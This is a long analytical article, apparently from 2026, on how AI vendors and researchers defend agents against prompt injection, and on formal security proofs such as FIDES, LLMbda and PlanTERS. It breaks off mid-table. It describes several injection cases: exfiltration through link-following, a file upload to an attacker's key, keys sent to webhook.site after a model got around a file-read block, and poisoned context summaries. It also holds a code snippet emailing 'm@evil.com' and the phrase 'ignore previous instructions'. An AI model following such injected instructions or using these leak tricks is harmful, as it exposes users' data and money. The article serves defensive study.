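When OpenAI released its Atlas browser in October 2025, its chief information security officer, Dane Stuckey, called prompt injection "a frontier, unsolved security problem". He described special training, overlapping filters and rapid responses to new attacks. Atlas also has a logged-out mode, in which the agent works without the user's credentials, and a watch mode, which is meant to pause the agent on sensitive sites when the user switches tabs. Willison tried watch mode on GitHub and on a banking site, and the agent did not pause on either.

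OpenAI went further in February 2026 with Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for business customers that it extended to personal accounts in June. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) states that the setting "deterministically disables" tools that an attacker could use to extract data. ChatGPT can then browse only cached copies of web pages, so browsing sends no live request outside OpenAI's network. The setting also turns off agent mode, Deep Research and file downloads.

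OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* lists the setting's limits. An instruction hidden in an uploaded file can still reach the model and make its answer wrong. Data may also leak through apps that remain enabled, and OpenAI doesn't guarantee that the setting prevents every leak. The setting doesn't affect network access in Codex, the company's coding agent, and users can turn it off for a single chat. Willison likes the design because no AI system decides what to block, but he infers from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings are not robust against a determined attacker. The setting disables agent mode, which makes ChatGPT closer to a tool than an agent, and OpenAI considers it unnecessary for most users.

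For features that stay on, OpenAI mainly warns the user. A developer who gives Codex internet access sees an "Elevated Risk" label and can limit that access to a list of domains. OpenAI's *Elevated Risk labels* acknowledges that the industry's safeguards do not yet fully deal with these risks.

### What Anthropic and Google have shipped

Anthropic's Claude chatbot has a tool for opening web pages. The tool accepts only addresses that the user typed or that a search returned, so an attacker can't make Claude add private data to an address and then visit it. But it used to accept links on pages it had already opened as well. Willison recounts that Ayush Paul built a site with a separate link for each letter of the alphabet and told Claude to spell out the user's name by following them. Each choice among 26 links can carry up to 4.7 bits. The site obtained the user's name, home city and employer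 without any violation of the tool's rules. Anthropic no longer lets the tool follow links it finds on the pages it opens.

Anthropic's office agent, Claude Cowork, limits outgoing traffic to a list of domains, which included Anthropic's own developer API. Researchers at the security firm PromptArmor planted instructions that made the agent upload the user's files there with an attacker's API key, so the attacker could download them later.

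Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, can run in a sandbox, where the operating system restricts which files and network addresses the agent can access. According to SC Media, users have to turn the sandbox on themselves. In August 2026 Anthropic made a different control, auto mode, the default on most plans. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* describes a classifier that checks each tool call and blocks those that look irreversible, destructive or aimed outside the user's environment. If the classifier blocks three calls in a row, or twenty in a session, and the agent can't make progress, the user has to approve actions again.

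Anthropic defends this choice by comparing the classifier with the people it replaces. In a study of 1,053 paid testers, only 13.6% refused a clearly dangerous command that the researchers had slipped in among ordinary requests. The classifier would have blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, which is much better than the testers did on this evidence, but it would still have let about one in nine through.

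Google's coding tool Antigravity also limited its browser agent to a list of domains. PromptArmor found that the default list included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address that records incoming requests. A web page posing as a software guide made the agent collect access keys and send them there. Antigravity was supposed to refuse to open the file containing the keys, so the model read it with a command-line tool instead.

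In August 2026 Google published a reference design for an agent that handles refunds. Saboo and Dong (2026), in *Build zero-trust AI agents with Google's Agent Development Kit*, assume that an attacker can fool the model. Their attacker has a damaged order worth $149, asks for a refund of $10,000, and tells the agent to run code that prints the server's secret settings. The design has three controls outside the model:

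1. The agent signs every database entry with its own key, so anyone who checks the signature can detect a later alteration.
2. Code written by the model runs in a sandbox with no network connection.
3. A gateway made of ordinary code inspects prompts, database commands and replies.

The signature doesn't stop a fooled agent, which would sign the $10,000 refund as readily as a correct one, so the gateway has to block the refund. The gateway in the published demonstration looks for phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" and blocks any order update that doesn't contain the text "149.00". An update that sets the refund to 9149.00 contains that text, so it would pass. A production system could instead read the amount as a number and compare it with the order total in the database. That check would need only a few lines of code, and it would support a worst-case claim about the size of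 refunds, provided the agent had no other way to issue them.

### Fixed rules and judgements

A deterministic control applies a fixed rule, so the same action always gets the same verdict, however persuasive the attacker's text is. A probabilistic control depends on the judgement of a model or a person. The table sorts the main controls into these two types.

| Control | Type | What can still go wrong |
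|---|---|---|
| Lockdown Mode's block on live browsing | Deterministic | False answers, leaks through enabled apps |
| Atlas's logged-out mode | Deterministic | Harm that needs no login |
| Lists of permitted domains | Deterministic | Leaks through a permitted domain |
| Claude Code's sandbox | Deterministic | Misuse of files and services the agent may use |
| Phrase list in Google's demonstration | Deterministic | Any rewording |
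| Training against injection | Probabilistic | Wording that the training did not cover |
| Auto mode's classifier | Probabilistic | Dangerous commands that look ordinary |
| User approval | Probabilistic | Requests approved without care |

A worst-case claim needs a rule that always applies and covers every way the bad event could happen. Vendors sometimes use "deterministic" as if it meant "secure", but determinism satisfies only the first condition. The phrase list, for example, blocks its listed phrases every time but misses every paraphrase. Lockdown Mode comes close to meeting both conditions for live web browsing, because OpenAI removed the ability altogether. A list of permitted domains comes less close, because somebody has to know what outsiders can do with each domain on it.

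### How repeated attempts weaken a defence

If each attempt succeeds independently with probability p, the chance of at least one success in k attempts is

1 − (1 − p)^k

For Claude Opus 4.5, this gives 38% after ten attempts, slightly above the measured 33.6%. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that the security firm Gray Swan ran the benchmark and that rates for competing models reached 92%.

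Measured success rates tend to fall below what the formula predicts because some scenarios are harder to attack than others. If attacks succeed 5% of the time in each of ten scenarios, an attacker will almost certainly have broken all ten after a hundred attempts at each. If attacks instead succeed half the time in one scenario and never in the other nine, the average for a single attempt is still 5%, but the attacker can never break more than one scenario in ten. Attackers who learn from their failures raise the measured rate.

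Newer models do much better. The closest comparison with Opus 4.5 is Claude Mythos Preview, which Gray Swan tested on an older benchmark, apparently the one used for that model. *Prompt Injection Robustness*, a set of notes on Anthropic's results, puts Mythos Preview's rate at 0.1% for one attempt and near zero for a hundred. *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier, 2026) quotes Anthropic's results for one and for 15 attempts, but these are less comparable because they come from a different benchmark. According to TechFeed, that benchmark replaced the older one because Claude models had almost stopped failing it. VentureBeat gives separate figures for Claude Opus 4.6 in coding and in operating a graphical interface.

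| Model | Test | One attempt | Repeated attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Older Gray Swan benchmark | 4.7% | 33.6% after 10, 63.0% after 100 |
| Claude Mythos Preview | Older Gray Swan benchmark | 0.1% | Near zero after 100 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding | 0% | 0% after 200 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, no added safeguards | 17.8% | 78.6% after 200 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Newer benchmark | 0.5% | 5.5% after 15 |
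| Claude Opus 5 | Newer benchmark | 0.2% | 2.0% after 15 |
| Muse Spark (Meta) | Newer benchmark | – | 16.5% after 15 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | Newer benchmark | – | 20.0% after 15 |

Opus 4.6's resistance to attack depended heavily on the setting. In the graphical interface, the attack success rate after 200 attempts was 78.6%, and added safeguards lowered it only to 57.1%. In coding, the model had a perfect result, but this did not carry over to later tests of Opus 4.8. VentureBeat (2026) reports that an attacker who adapted to the model succeeded in 7.03% of single attempts in a coding environment, or 2.09% with safeguards.

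The figures that Schneier quotes for Opus 5 stop at 15 attempts. If each attempt independently had a 0.2% chance of success, the chance of at least one break would be 18% after a hundred attempts and 86% after a thousand. The true rates could be well below these if most scenarios resist every attack, but an attacker can spread the attempts over many victims. If one message reached a million assistants and worked 0.2% of the time, it would hijack 2,000 of them.

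Some recent tests recorded no successful attacks. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports none in 129 browser scenarios, though it also cites OpenAI's admission the previous December that prompt injection may never be fully solved. To test auto mode, Anthropic commissioned an outside firm to run 72 scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts on Opus 5 succeeded. By the formula that Nazeri and colleagues use, 720 independent trials without a success are consistent with a true success rate as high as about 0.7%. But ten runs of the same scenario are not independent, and if the repeats added no information, the upper limit would be about 7%.

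*Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* (Crosley, 2026) reports that, within weeks, the security researcher Johann Rehberger published attacks on Opus 5 in auto mode that worked in three or four of five runs. Five runs are too few to estimate a general rate, but they show that the zero result did not extend to attacks outside the test. Willison had described another possible gap when Anthropic announced its result. A software package could include instructions for the agent to download files with a helper program before running the tests, and that program could steal the data. The command would look like an ordinary programming step, so a classifier would probably not block it.

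### Whether anyone has adopted isolation

The SC Media article states that no mainstream agent product, including Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot Agent and Gemini CLI, had adopted CaMeL or the dual-LLM pattern. It advises companies to assume that attackers will take over the model and to limit the damage with sandboxes, separate storage for passwords and controls on outgoing traffic. Sophos had published the text on its own site before 20 May 2026, when Microsoft changed this situation.

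Microsoft has released FIDES as part of Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) explains it with an agent that sorts bug reports. A stranger's report contains a fake system message telling the agent to read a file of passwords and post them as a public comment. Even if the model follows this instruction, the software has labelled the file private and the comment tool accepts only public data, so the call fails. By default, the framework also hides untrusted text from the planner, as Costa and colleagues proposed, so any developer can now install the isolated design.

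Microsoft calls it experimental, though, and developers have to turn it on and label their own data sources. If they forget to label one, the framework treats its data as trusted and public, which is the least safe assumption. They can also have the framework ask the user about a call that breaks the policy instead of refusing it, but the protection then depends on the user's judgement again.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes similar support in GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the command line. Users must set a flag to enable it, and it covers only selected GitHub tools. Microsoft aims to ask for approval less often, for example only when a message would show information to somebody who could not already read it. In that arrangement, fixed rules handle most calls and people decide the few that the rules can't settle.

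Google has published a design that isolates part of a system. In its warranty-claim example, one agent reads the free-text warranty terms. That agent receives only checked inputs, such as serial numbers, and returns a simple status, such as "Covered", to the agent that handles the claim. A status this short leaves little room for an injected instruction.

The statement that nobody had adopted isolation was therefore only just out of date by late 2026. One mainstream framework offered isolation as an experimental option, and one mainstream coding agent had partial support for it behind a flag. The controls that Anthropic and OpenAI turned on by default still relied largely on the model, a classifier or the user judging correctly.

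## What the proofs establish and what they take on trust

The published proofs about isolated agents, including the one for FIDES, establish four different properties, and an agent can satisfy one of them while leaking data that another would have protected. Every proof also assumes facts about labels, policies, users and software.

### Noninterference

The oldest and strictest of the four properties is noninterference. Fix an observer, such as the stranger who emails the assistant. Let s be the user's secret data, a the messages the stranger sends, and Obs(s, a) everything the stranger sees in return. The system is noninterferent if

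Obs(s₁, a) = Obs(s₂, a) for all secrets s₁ and s₂ and every a

In that case, nothing the stranger sees depends on the user's data. The same formula describes integrity when the roles are changed. If the arguments of a payment stay the same whatever the untrusted inputs are, no attacker can influence the payment.

Few useful agents satisfy noninterference. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that answers emailed meeting requests with its user's free times. The user wants those replies, but they depend on a private calendar, so the assistant violates noninterference. The usual remedy is declassification, where somebody lists what the system may release for each task. Costa and colleagues rejected noninterference for FIDES because it would in effect forbid any call with public effects after a call that might have read a secret.

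### Explicit secrecy

The confidentiality theorem behind FIDES uses a weaker property, explicit secrecy. Let d be the contents of all the data that tools can read or write. As the agent runs, its tool calls change d, and g stands for their combined effect, so that g(d) is the data afterwards. Write d₁ =ₗ d₂ if two sets of data agree on everything public. Explicit secrecy requires, for every partial run that starts from d₁ and has effect g,

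if d₁ =ₗ d₂, then g(d₁) =ₗ g(d₂)

The same g appears on both sides, so the definition holds the agent's actual calls fixed and compares what they would have written under different secrets. It does not account for the possibility that different secrets would have led the agent to make different calls.

Suppose the agent forwards Charlie's private email to the stranger. g copies the email into the stranger's mailbox, so a different email would have produced a different copy, and the run violates explicit secrecy. Suppose instead that the agent checks whether the email mentions a takeover and sends the stranger the word "yes" or "no". In a run that sends "yes", g writes "yes" whatever the email contains, so the run satisfies explicit secrecy even though the stranger has learned that the email mentions a takeover.

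Costa and colleagues acknowledge that someone who sees the sequence of calls may infer limited information. Their model also leaves out timing and network packet length, and it treats the language model as deterministic. They regard explicit secrecy as a practical compromise, which web browsers and the Android tracking tool TaintDroid had already adopted. FIDES can also refuse calls that come from an untrusted conversation, and this integrity check would stop many "yes" or "no" attacks that the secrecy theorem alone does not rule out.

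The amount leaked depends on how often the agent can repeat the leak. A program that loops over the bits of a password and sends "yes" or "no" for each one reveals the whole password without copying it. Garby and colleagues therefore consider explicit secrecy weakest for agents that write and run code.

### The branch not taken

To stop such leaks, the software has to track conditions as well as data. CaMeL's interpreter does some of this. If an injected instruction makes the agent email an outsider only when a customer's balance exceeds some threshold, the interpreter notices that the decision to send depends on the balance, and refuses the call. Garby and colleagues found a way round this check, using a trick that Fenton described in 1974. In outline, the program is:

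```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The interpreter raises a variable's label when a branch that depends on a secret changes the variable. If the program skips the branch, the label stays as it was.

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance not above it |
|---|---|---|
| First `if` | Runs: tmp becomes False and secret | Skipped: tmp stays True and public |
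| Second `if` | Skipped: rich stays True and public | Runs: rich becomes False and public |
| Third `if` | The email goes out | No email |

In both columns "rich" ends up public, so the interpreter does not block the email. But the value of "rich" matches the secret exactly, so the outsider can learn whether the customer is rich by waiting to see whether the email arrives.

The standard repair is to stop the program as soon as a branch that depends on a secret tries to change something public. In the example, the program would stop at the first "if" when the balance is above the threshold and carry on otherwise. This still reveals one bit to anyone who can tell whether the program stopped. Most information-flow systems allow this leak, because preventing it would require proving that programs finish.

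Retries can leak many bits instead of just the one. CaMeL runs its interpreter inside an ordinary Python loop that tries again after a failure, and nothing tracks the information that passes through that loop. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal another bit. If each attempt tests the balance against a new threshold, the attempts together reveal the whole balance. A series of yes/no answers can reveal a password-reset code in the same way. CaMeL's developers censor the error messages to limit the leak, but they have no proof that this works. Garby and colleagues avoid the problem in their agent, Randori, by having the model write and repair its program against artificial data. Only the finished program runs on the real account.

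### Noninterference for programs that call a model

Randori runs in LLMbda, a small programming language by Garby and colleagues in which prompting a model, copying its conversation and clearing it are basic operations. They proved that every LLMbda program satisfies termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, and verified the proof with the proof checker Lean. "Termination-insensitive" means that the property does not cover what an observer can learn from whether the program finishes. "Probabilistic" means that it compares the probability of each result, since a model may answer the same prompt differently each time.

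Take one program and two secrets. For each result q that the observer can see, let μ₁(q) be the probability that the program finishes with q under the first secret, and μ₂(q) the same under the second. These probabilities may add up to less than one, because some runs never finish or break a policy and stop. The property requires some ω such that

μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q) and μ₂(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1

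The smallest possible ω takes the larger of the two probabilities for each result, so the condition amounts to

Σ max(μ₁(q), μ₂(q)) ≤ 1

If an agent always sends "yes" under one secret and "no" under the other, the sum is 2, and the agent violates the property. If it sends "yes" under one secret and always stops under the other, the sum is 1, which the property permits. When both programs always finish, the condition holds only if the two sets of probabilities are identical, in which case nothing leaks.

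The theorem also limits how much stopping can reveal about the secret. The statistical distance between the two cases, ½ Σ |μ₁(q) − μ₂(q)|, is at most the average of their probabilities of not finishing. If an agent fails to finish in 2% of runs under each secret, switching secrets changes the chance of any visible outcome by at most two percentage points.

Garby and colleagues first tried a simpler definition that compares only the runs that finish, but it wrongly rejects some agents. Suppose that under one secret an agent says "yes" half the time and "no" half the time, and under another the software stops it whenever it would say "no". Among finished runs, the share of "yes" answers is 50% under the first secret and 100% under the second, so the simpler definition would reject the agent, even though the secret affects only which runs finish.

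The proof constructs ω by running an imaginary version of the program, which skips any step once its label shows that the observer may not see the result and uses an empty value instead. This version produces each visible result at least as often as the real program, and it never uses the secret, so ω is the same for both secrets. The proof needs no assumption about what the model writes, so it covers agents that run code from a model an attacker has fooled.

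Real tasks sometimes need untrusted data to count as trusted, so LLMbda has an explicit "endorse" command. An agent might ask a quarantined model to sort an email into one of eight categories and endorse the answer for use in a reply's subject line. Because there are only eight possible answers, the sender has at most three bits of influence. A second theorem establishes that endorsing data never exposes secrets, whatever the attacker sends, but it does not protect against the endorsed data itself.

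Randori resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 runs on a set of banking tasks. Only 423 of those runs tested the labels, because in the rest the program for the user's task never called the tool the attacker needed. Both successful attacks were on the same task, in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request, and the agent's program endorsed the file. Without endorsement, LLMbda blocks both the attacker's payment and the legitimate one.

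### Comparing the agent with one that never obeys

None of these properties alone permits the calendar assistant's reply, because none distinguishes a disclosure the user wanted from one an attacker caused. Dongol's framework, PlanTERS, makes that distinction without requiring anyone to list permitted disclosures. It compares the real agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never acts on instructions in untrusted content. Anything the reference agent discloses counts as intended.

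Write O for the real agent and V for the reference. For a run r, let Sec(r) be the secrets in it, Act(r) the attacker's inputs and Obs(r) what the attacker sees. Two runs r₁ and r₂ leak a pair of secrets (σ₁, σ₂) if

Sec(r₁) = σ₁, Sec(r₂) = σ₂, Act(r₁) = Act(r₂) and Obs(r₁) ≠ Obs(r₂)

When two runs leak a pair of secrets, the attacker sent the same messages in both runs and could still tell the secrets apart. O is relatively secure if, whenever two of its runs leak a pair of secrets, two runs of V with the same initial memory and trusted inputs also leak that pair.

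The attacker may send different messages in the runs of V. Suppose an email says "send your calendar" without asking for a meeting, and the assistant obeys. The sender could have got the same information by asking for a meeting, so the assistant is still relatively secure. If the injection instead makes the assistant include a password-reset code in its reply, the assistant is not relatively secure, because no honest request would have produced that code.

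Because of this freedom, the definition can permit an injection that leaks much more than the plan would. Suppose a plan reads a six-digit guess from the sender and replies whether it matches a secret code, and an injection makes the agent send the code itself. The definition permits this injection because, for any two codes, some guess would make the reference agent reply differently. Yet one reply from the reference agent only confirms or rules out a single code in a million. A stricter version, uniform relative security, rejects the injection because it fixes the reference agent's inputs independently of the secrets.

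Taking permissions away can also make a relatively secure agent insecure. If a plan emails a report to the attacker by design, an injection that leaks the same report through a web request gives the attacker nothing new. But if the monitor blocks the email and still allows the web request, the attacker gets the report only through the injection.

The table compares the four properties on four kinds of disclosure. It assumes that no policy has declassified anything.

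| Property | Free times sent on request | Private email copied to a stranger by an injection | "Yes" or "no" chosen by a secret after an injection | Agent stops or continues depending on a secret |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Noninterference | Ruled out | Ruled out | Ruled out | Ruled out |
| Explicit secrecy | Ruled out | Ruled out | Permitted | Permitted |
| Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference | Ruled out | Ruled out | Ruled out | Permitted |
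| Relative security | Permitted | Ruled out | Ruled out | Not ruled out in general |

Relative security concerns only leaks. A proof of it does not rule out an injection that deletes the user's files or pays the wrong account without revealing anything, so it offers no protection against the forged invoice.

### Why tools have to go before the first untrusted read

Dongol's main result concerns a fence, which is a monitor that revokes certain tools when the agent reads untrusted content. Every plan is relatively secure if the fence covers every tool an injection can call and nothing grants those tools again. The plan's own calls get the same answers in the real agent and the reference agent. The monitor refuses every injected call because its tool has been revoked, and the refusal has no visible effect. The attacker therefore sees exactly what the reference agent would have shown.

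It matters when the monitor starts blocking email if, for example, the plan itself controls this with a lock and the agent's memory already holds some private data from earlier work.

| Order of steps | What an injected "send" can leak |
|---|---|
| Read the email, read a secret, lock | The secret and the earlier data |
| Read the email, lock, read a secret | The earlier data |
| Lock, read the email, read a secret | Nothing |

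Relative security and the word "fence" both come from research on processors that run instructions ahead of time, a behavior the Spectre attacks exploited. On those processors, a fence can go just before the leaking code, because that code is already in the program. An injection adds its own leaking call, which may come at any moment after the model reads the injection, so a fence placed later than that reading step leaves a gap.

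The theorem assumes that each injection is a single tool call. If an injection can run a whole program, it can overwrite a variable that the plan later sends, and the fence helps only if a sandbox discards such changes. The theorem also assumes that the model obeys injections on a schedule fixed in advance. An email that tells the model to wait unless the balance is above $10,000 breaks this assumption. A fence would probably still refuse the resulting call, but the theorem doesn't cover this case.

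An agent that handles one request after another needs its tools back. Restoring them at the user's next message is unsafe, because the conversation still contains the earlier email and the model may still follow instructions in it. Dongol proves that the monitor can safely restore the tools if the model starts a new session that keeps nothing from the old one.

A monitor that refuses every call also passes the test, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and is equally useless and discloses just as little. One of Dongol's own positive results partly has this problem. A model of CaMeL's tag check is secure against every injection, but only because it refuses every reply that contains private data, including the reply the user wanted. A proof of security therefore needs a separate check that the agent can still do its job.

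### Approving a tool and approving a call

Some tasks require an agent to use a tool after it has read untrusted content, and the common solution is to ask the user for approval. Suppose Alice's agent reads an email, waits for Alice to approve a reply and then sends it. The agent's memory also holds private data that is not sent at any step of the plan.

If Alice's approval means "the agent may send one message", an injection in an email can use that permission before the plan sends the reply. After Alice approves, the model follows the injected instructions and sends the private data to the attacker. The monitor then blocks the message Alice wrote because the permission has been used. A limit on the number of messages fails in the same way, unless the plan uses up the limit before it reads anything untrusted.

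If Alice approves an exact call, including its recipient and text, an injected call gets through only if it is identical. Dongol proves this secure against every injection that calls the sending tool, provided the model doesn't keep obeying the injection forever. But the proof assumes the attacker sees the messages and their order but not their timing. If the private data matches Alice's reply, the injected call sends it one step early, so an attacker who can time the messages learns that the two match. This matters mainly when the data has few possible values, such as yes or no.

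The choice of attacker affects other results as well. Suppose a monitor permits web requests only to a newsletter's address. An injection can trigger a request to the newsletter if a secret bit is 0 and to a forbidden address if it is 1. The monitor blocks the second request, so a recipient can learn the bit from whether an extra message arrives. The weaker attacker in PlanTERS compares only runs in which the same number of messages arrive between reads, so a proof against that attacker does not rule out this leak.

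### What a deployment has to guarantee

The theorems in PlanTERS apply to a real agent only if its software meets seven conditions. The table lists each condition with an example of something that would violate it.

| Condition | What would break it |
|---|---|
| Trusted software runs the plan as written | A model that can skip or change steps |
| Every call and untrusted read goes through the monitor | A browser the monitor doesn't control |
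| Content reaches the model only after the monitor allows the read | A tool that loads a page before asking |
| Refused calls have no visible effect | A public error message or log |
| The attacker can't see the agent's internal steps | A displayed reply that loads an image from the attacker's server |
| A fresh session clears everything the model kept | A memory feature that carries text between sessions |
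| The attacker can't write to trusted sources | A calendar that accepts invitations from outsiders |

Dongol also excludes tools whose answer depends on the question, such as a search engine that the attacker runs. Many office agents have a calendar open to outsiders, a search tool and some form of memory, so they would need changes before the theorems applied to them.

Narisetty and colleagues trace the conditions to the reference monitor that Anderson described in the 1970s, which has to check every access, resist tampering and be small enough to verify. In most published agent defences, the final check is ordinary code that could meet these requirements, but its inputs are harder to trust.

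### Labels and policies

A monitor that compares labels depends on those labels being correct. FIDES computes the label of a tool's result from lists of the data the tool may read and change. If the developer of a search tool forgets to list the private files it searches, its results can be labeled public, and the proof then doesn't cover the private data in them.

Narisetty and colleagues call label assignment the trusted base of the whole approach and consider it under-specified. Saltzer and Schroeder wrote in 1975 that a system should refuse by default, so that mistakes make it less useful rather than less safe. Microsoft's version of FIDES does the reverse by treating unlabelled data as trusted and public.

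LLMbda has the same weakness. Its theorems cover every program a model can write, but Garby and colleagues note that the developer of the tool library must still label sources correctly and put a check in front of every sensitive action. For their tests, they simulated the bank and its files in LLMbda itself, and they list the connection to real outside tools as a limitation.

Somebody also has to write the policy. Since people rarely want to write rules for every request, some systems leave this to a model. In Progent, a model reads the user's request and writes a list of permitted calls, which ordinary code then enforces. Even perfect enforcement doesn't help if the list is wrong. For example, Progent checks only the arguments that the list mentions, so a rule that limits the amount of a transfer but not its recipient lets the agent pay anyone.

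Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, measured how a fixed policy limits what agents can complete. Progent normally writes its policy once per session. When a user then asked for a second task, agents completed it in only 7 of 60 sessions. With a new policy for each request, they completed it in 41, but Progent then has to decide at every request what the user has asked for.

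### Whose words count as the user's

If a user pastes a hostile document into a request, the document is labeled as trusted from the start. None of the four properties in this section protects against this, because they all assume that inputs have been correctly divided into trusted and untrusted.

In long conversations, the software can make the same mistake without the user's involvement. When a conversation nears the model's length limit, the agent's software compacts it by having a model summarise the earlier part, and the agent continues from the summary. In all 1,108 automatic compactions that Fei and colleagues recorded in Claude Code and Codex, the software inserted the summary as a message from the user. A system that writes its policy from the user's latest message may then write it from a summary that contains an attacker's text.

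Suppose a user asks a banking agent how much they spent in March, and one transaction contains an instruction to pay an attacker. Progent blocks the transfer because the question doesn't call for one. After context compaction, the summary lists the blocked transfer as unfinished work, and the next policy permits exactly one transfer, to the attacker's account.

Fei and colleagues tested whether the summary's position was the cause by giving Progent different inputs after the same attacked conversations. The table shows how often the new policy granted something the old one did not and how often it named the attacker's account.

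| Input to the policy writer | New permissions | Attacker named |
|---|---|---|
| A short "please continue" from the user | 0 of 30 | 0 of 30 |
| The user's request, restated | 5 of 30 | 0 of 30 |
| The summary, as a user message | 21 of 30 | 16 of 30 |
| The same summary, as a tool result | 0 of 28 | 0 of 28 |

The summary text was identical in the last two rows, so the difference came from its position. In a larger test where a small model wrote the summaries, attacks that Progent had blocked succeeded after compaction in 31 of 100 cases, and in 26 in a repeat of the test. Without any defence, they succeeded in 33. These results apply to the version of Progent that writes a new policy for each request, not to its normal setting.

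Better summaries help only against some attacks. When a summary described the attacker's account as suspicious or as part of an injection, the policy named that account in 7 of 230 cases, compared with 349 of 536 without such a warning. Stronger models often add warnings to hidden instructions but rarely to false information that contains no instruction. In one test, the user had stated the landlord's account, and an attacker's notice gave a different one. When the user later asked to pay the rent, policies written from the user's own words never allowed payment to the attacker's account. Policies written from a strong model's summary allowed it in 91% of cases with one policy writer and 59% with another.

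Leaving the attacker's account number out of the summary does not always block the transfer either. Of 410 banking policies written from summaries without that number, 78 still allowed the transfer, usually because they did not restrict the recipient. In a test of 80 policies with no recipient restriction, the agent read the poisoned record again and completed the attacker's call 26 times.

Fei and colleagues prove a general limit for any system that sees only text and not who wrote it. Let p_L be the probability that the policy accepts an account number when a legitimate source wrote the record, and p_A the probability when an attacker did. Let P_L and P_A be the corresponding distributions of everything the system reads. Then

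p_L − p_A ≤ TV(P_L, P_A)

where TV, the total variation distance, is the largest difference between the probabilities that the two distributions give to any event. If the attacker copies the format and typical values of real records perfectly, the distance is zero, and the system accepts forged accounts exactly as often as genuine ones. No improvement in the wording of the summary changes that.

The remedy is to record which messages the user sent. The software attaches a cryptographic tag to each of the user's messages on arrival and carries those messages unchanged through compaction. The agent still reads the summary, but the policy writer receives only the tagged messages. If any message is missing, altered or out of order, the new policy permits nothing. No attacker's action succeeded in 40 attacked conversations, and the design also withstood eight attacks made specifically against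 it. The test is small, but the proof covers more than the test does, as long as the agent cannot reach the keys and the software tags only what the user sent. The software also tags text that the user pastes in. If the user asks the agent to pay whatever account a document gives, the tags cannot show whether the document is genuine.

### People who click "approve"

When a policy doesn't determine whether a call is allowed, most systems ask the user, and the proof assumes the answer is correct. Costa and colleagues warn of confirmation fatigue and of attackers who talk users into agreeing. In the best measurement of how users respond, Anthropic's study of paid testers, only 13.6% refused a clearly dangerous command. If they are typical, asking the user stops about one dangerous call in seven. Real users may do better because their own files are at stake, but they also see many more requests.

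Approving exact calls takes more effort than approving tools. Alice can allow the email tool with one click, but to approve each exact call she has to read the whole reply and check the recipient. Exact-call approval has the stronger theorem, but it also depends more on users paying attention, and the measurements suggest they don't.

### The code that enforces the rules

A theorem about a design doesn't cover mistakes in the program that implements it. CaMeL's published security argument is informal, and its developers call a formal treatment a "crucial direction" for later work. Besides the skipped branch and the retry loop, Garby and colleagues found that inserting untrusted values into text could make CaMeL treat them as trusted. They found all three problems by reading the code closely, not through the benchmark attacks that CaMeL had resisted.

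LLMbda comes closest to closing this gap. A third theorem shows that the program that calls the model behaves as the mathematical definition requires, so the security proof applies to running software. The guarantee still depends on trusting Lean itself, the code that sends requests over the network, and the tools, and on assuming that the model's answers follow fixed probabilities given the conversation.

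PlanTERS proves more about particular defences but less about real software. Dongol and an AI coding assistant wrote about 31,600 lines of definitions and proofs covering 25 example agents, and the proof checker Isabelle/HOL verified the proofs. Readers don't have to trust the assistant's proofs, because the checker would have rejected a faulty one, but they do have to check that the definitions describe a real agent. The examples are deliberately tiny test cases, not the code of FIDES or CaMeL.

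## How much usefulness the restrictions cost

A security proof doesn't show how many ordinary tasks an agent can still finish, and critics of restriction expect few. Costa and colleagues worked out which tasks an isolated planner cannot do in principle, and several teams have measured the loss in practice.

### Tasks that one fixed plan can solve

An isolated planner copes best with data-independent tasks. To state the definition exactly, let D be the set of situations the agent might find, such as all the mailboxes it might open. For each d in D, let S(d) be the set of action sequences that would do the job correctly in that situation. The task is data-independent if

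⋂ S(d) over all d in D ≠ ∅

so that at least one sequence works in every situation, and data-dependent otherwise.

Forwarding the three newest emails passes this test. Creating a calendar event only if one of them asks for a meeting fails it, because no single sequence is correct in both cases.

Summarising the emails for a colleague is also data-independent, but a model has to read them. A planner that can only pass variables along cannot do this properly, so it needs a quarantined model to write the summary.

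Costa and colleagues sorted the 97 user tasks in the *AgentDojo* benchmark into these classes by hand. The benchmark simulates an office workspace, a travel service, a bank and the messaging program Slack, with tasks such as managing an email client or booking a trip. Software checks at the end of each run whether the agent met the user's goal. They counted 26 tasks in which one fixed sequence works without any model reading untrusted text, 51 that have a fixed sequence but need a quarantined reader, and 20 that are data-dependent. The data-dependent tasks make up 5% of the workspace tasks and 10% of the travel tasks, but about 43% of those in banking and Slack. Many of the banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it.

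A planner that can write conditions can still handle some data-dependent tasks, including the meeting request. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) counts only six AgentDojo tasks that require dynamic planning, where the agent has to change its plan after seeing what a tool returned. If those six are among the 20, a planner could write the branches for the other 14 in advance. A strict policy may still block those tasks, because untrusted data would determine which branch runs.

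### What FIDES completes

Costa and colleagues ran FIDES on AgentDojo with two OpenAI models, GPT-4o and the early reasoning model o1. Both date from 2024 and are far behind current models. For most tools with lasting effects, the policies required the decision to call the tool to come from a trusted conversation, but allowed its arguments to be untrusted. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed without an attack, averaged over five runs.

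| Suite | GPT-4o, plain agent | GPT-4o, plain with policies | GPT-4o, FIDES with policies | o1, plain agent | o1, plain with policies | o1, FIDES with policies |
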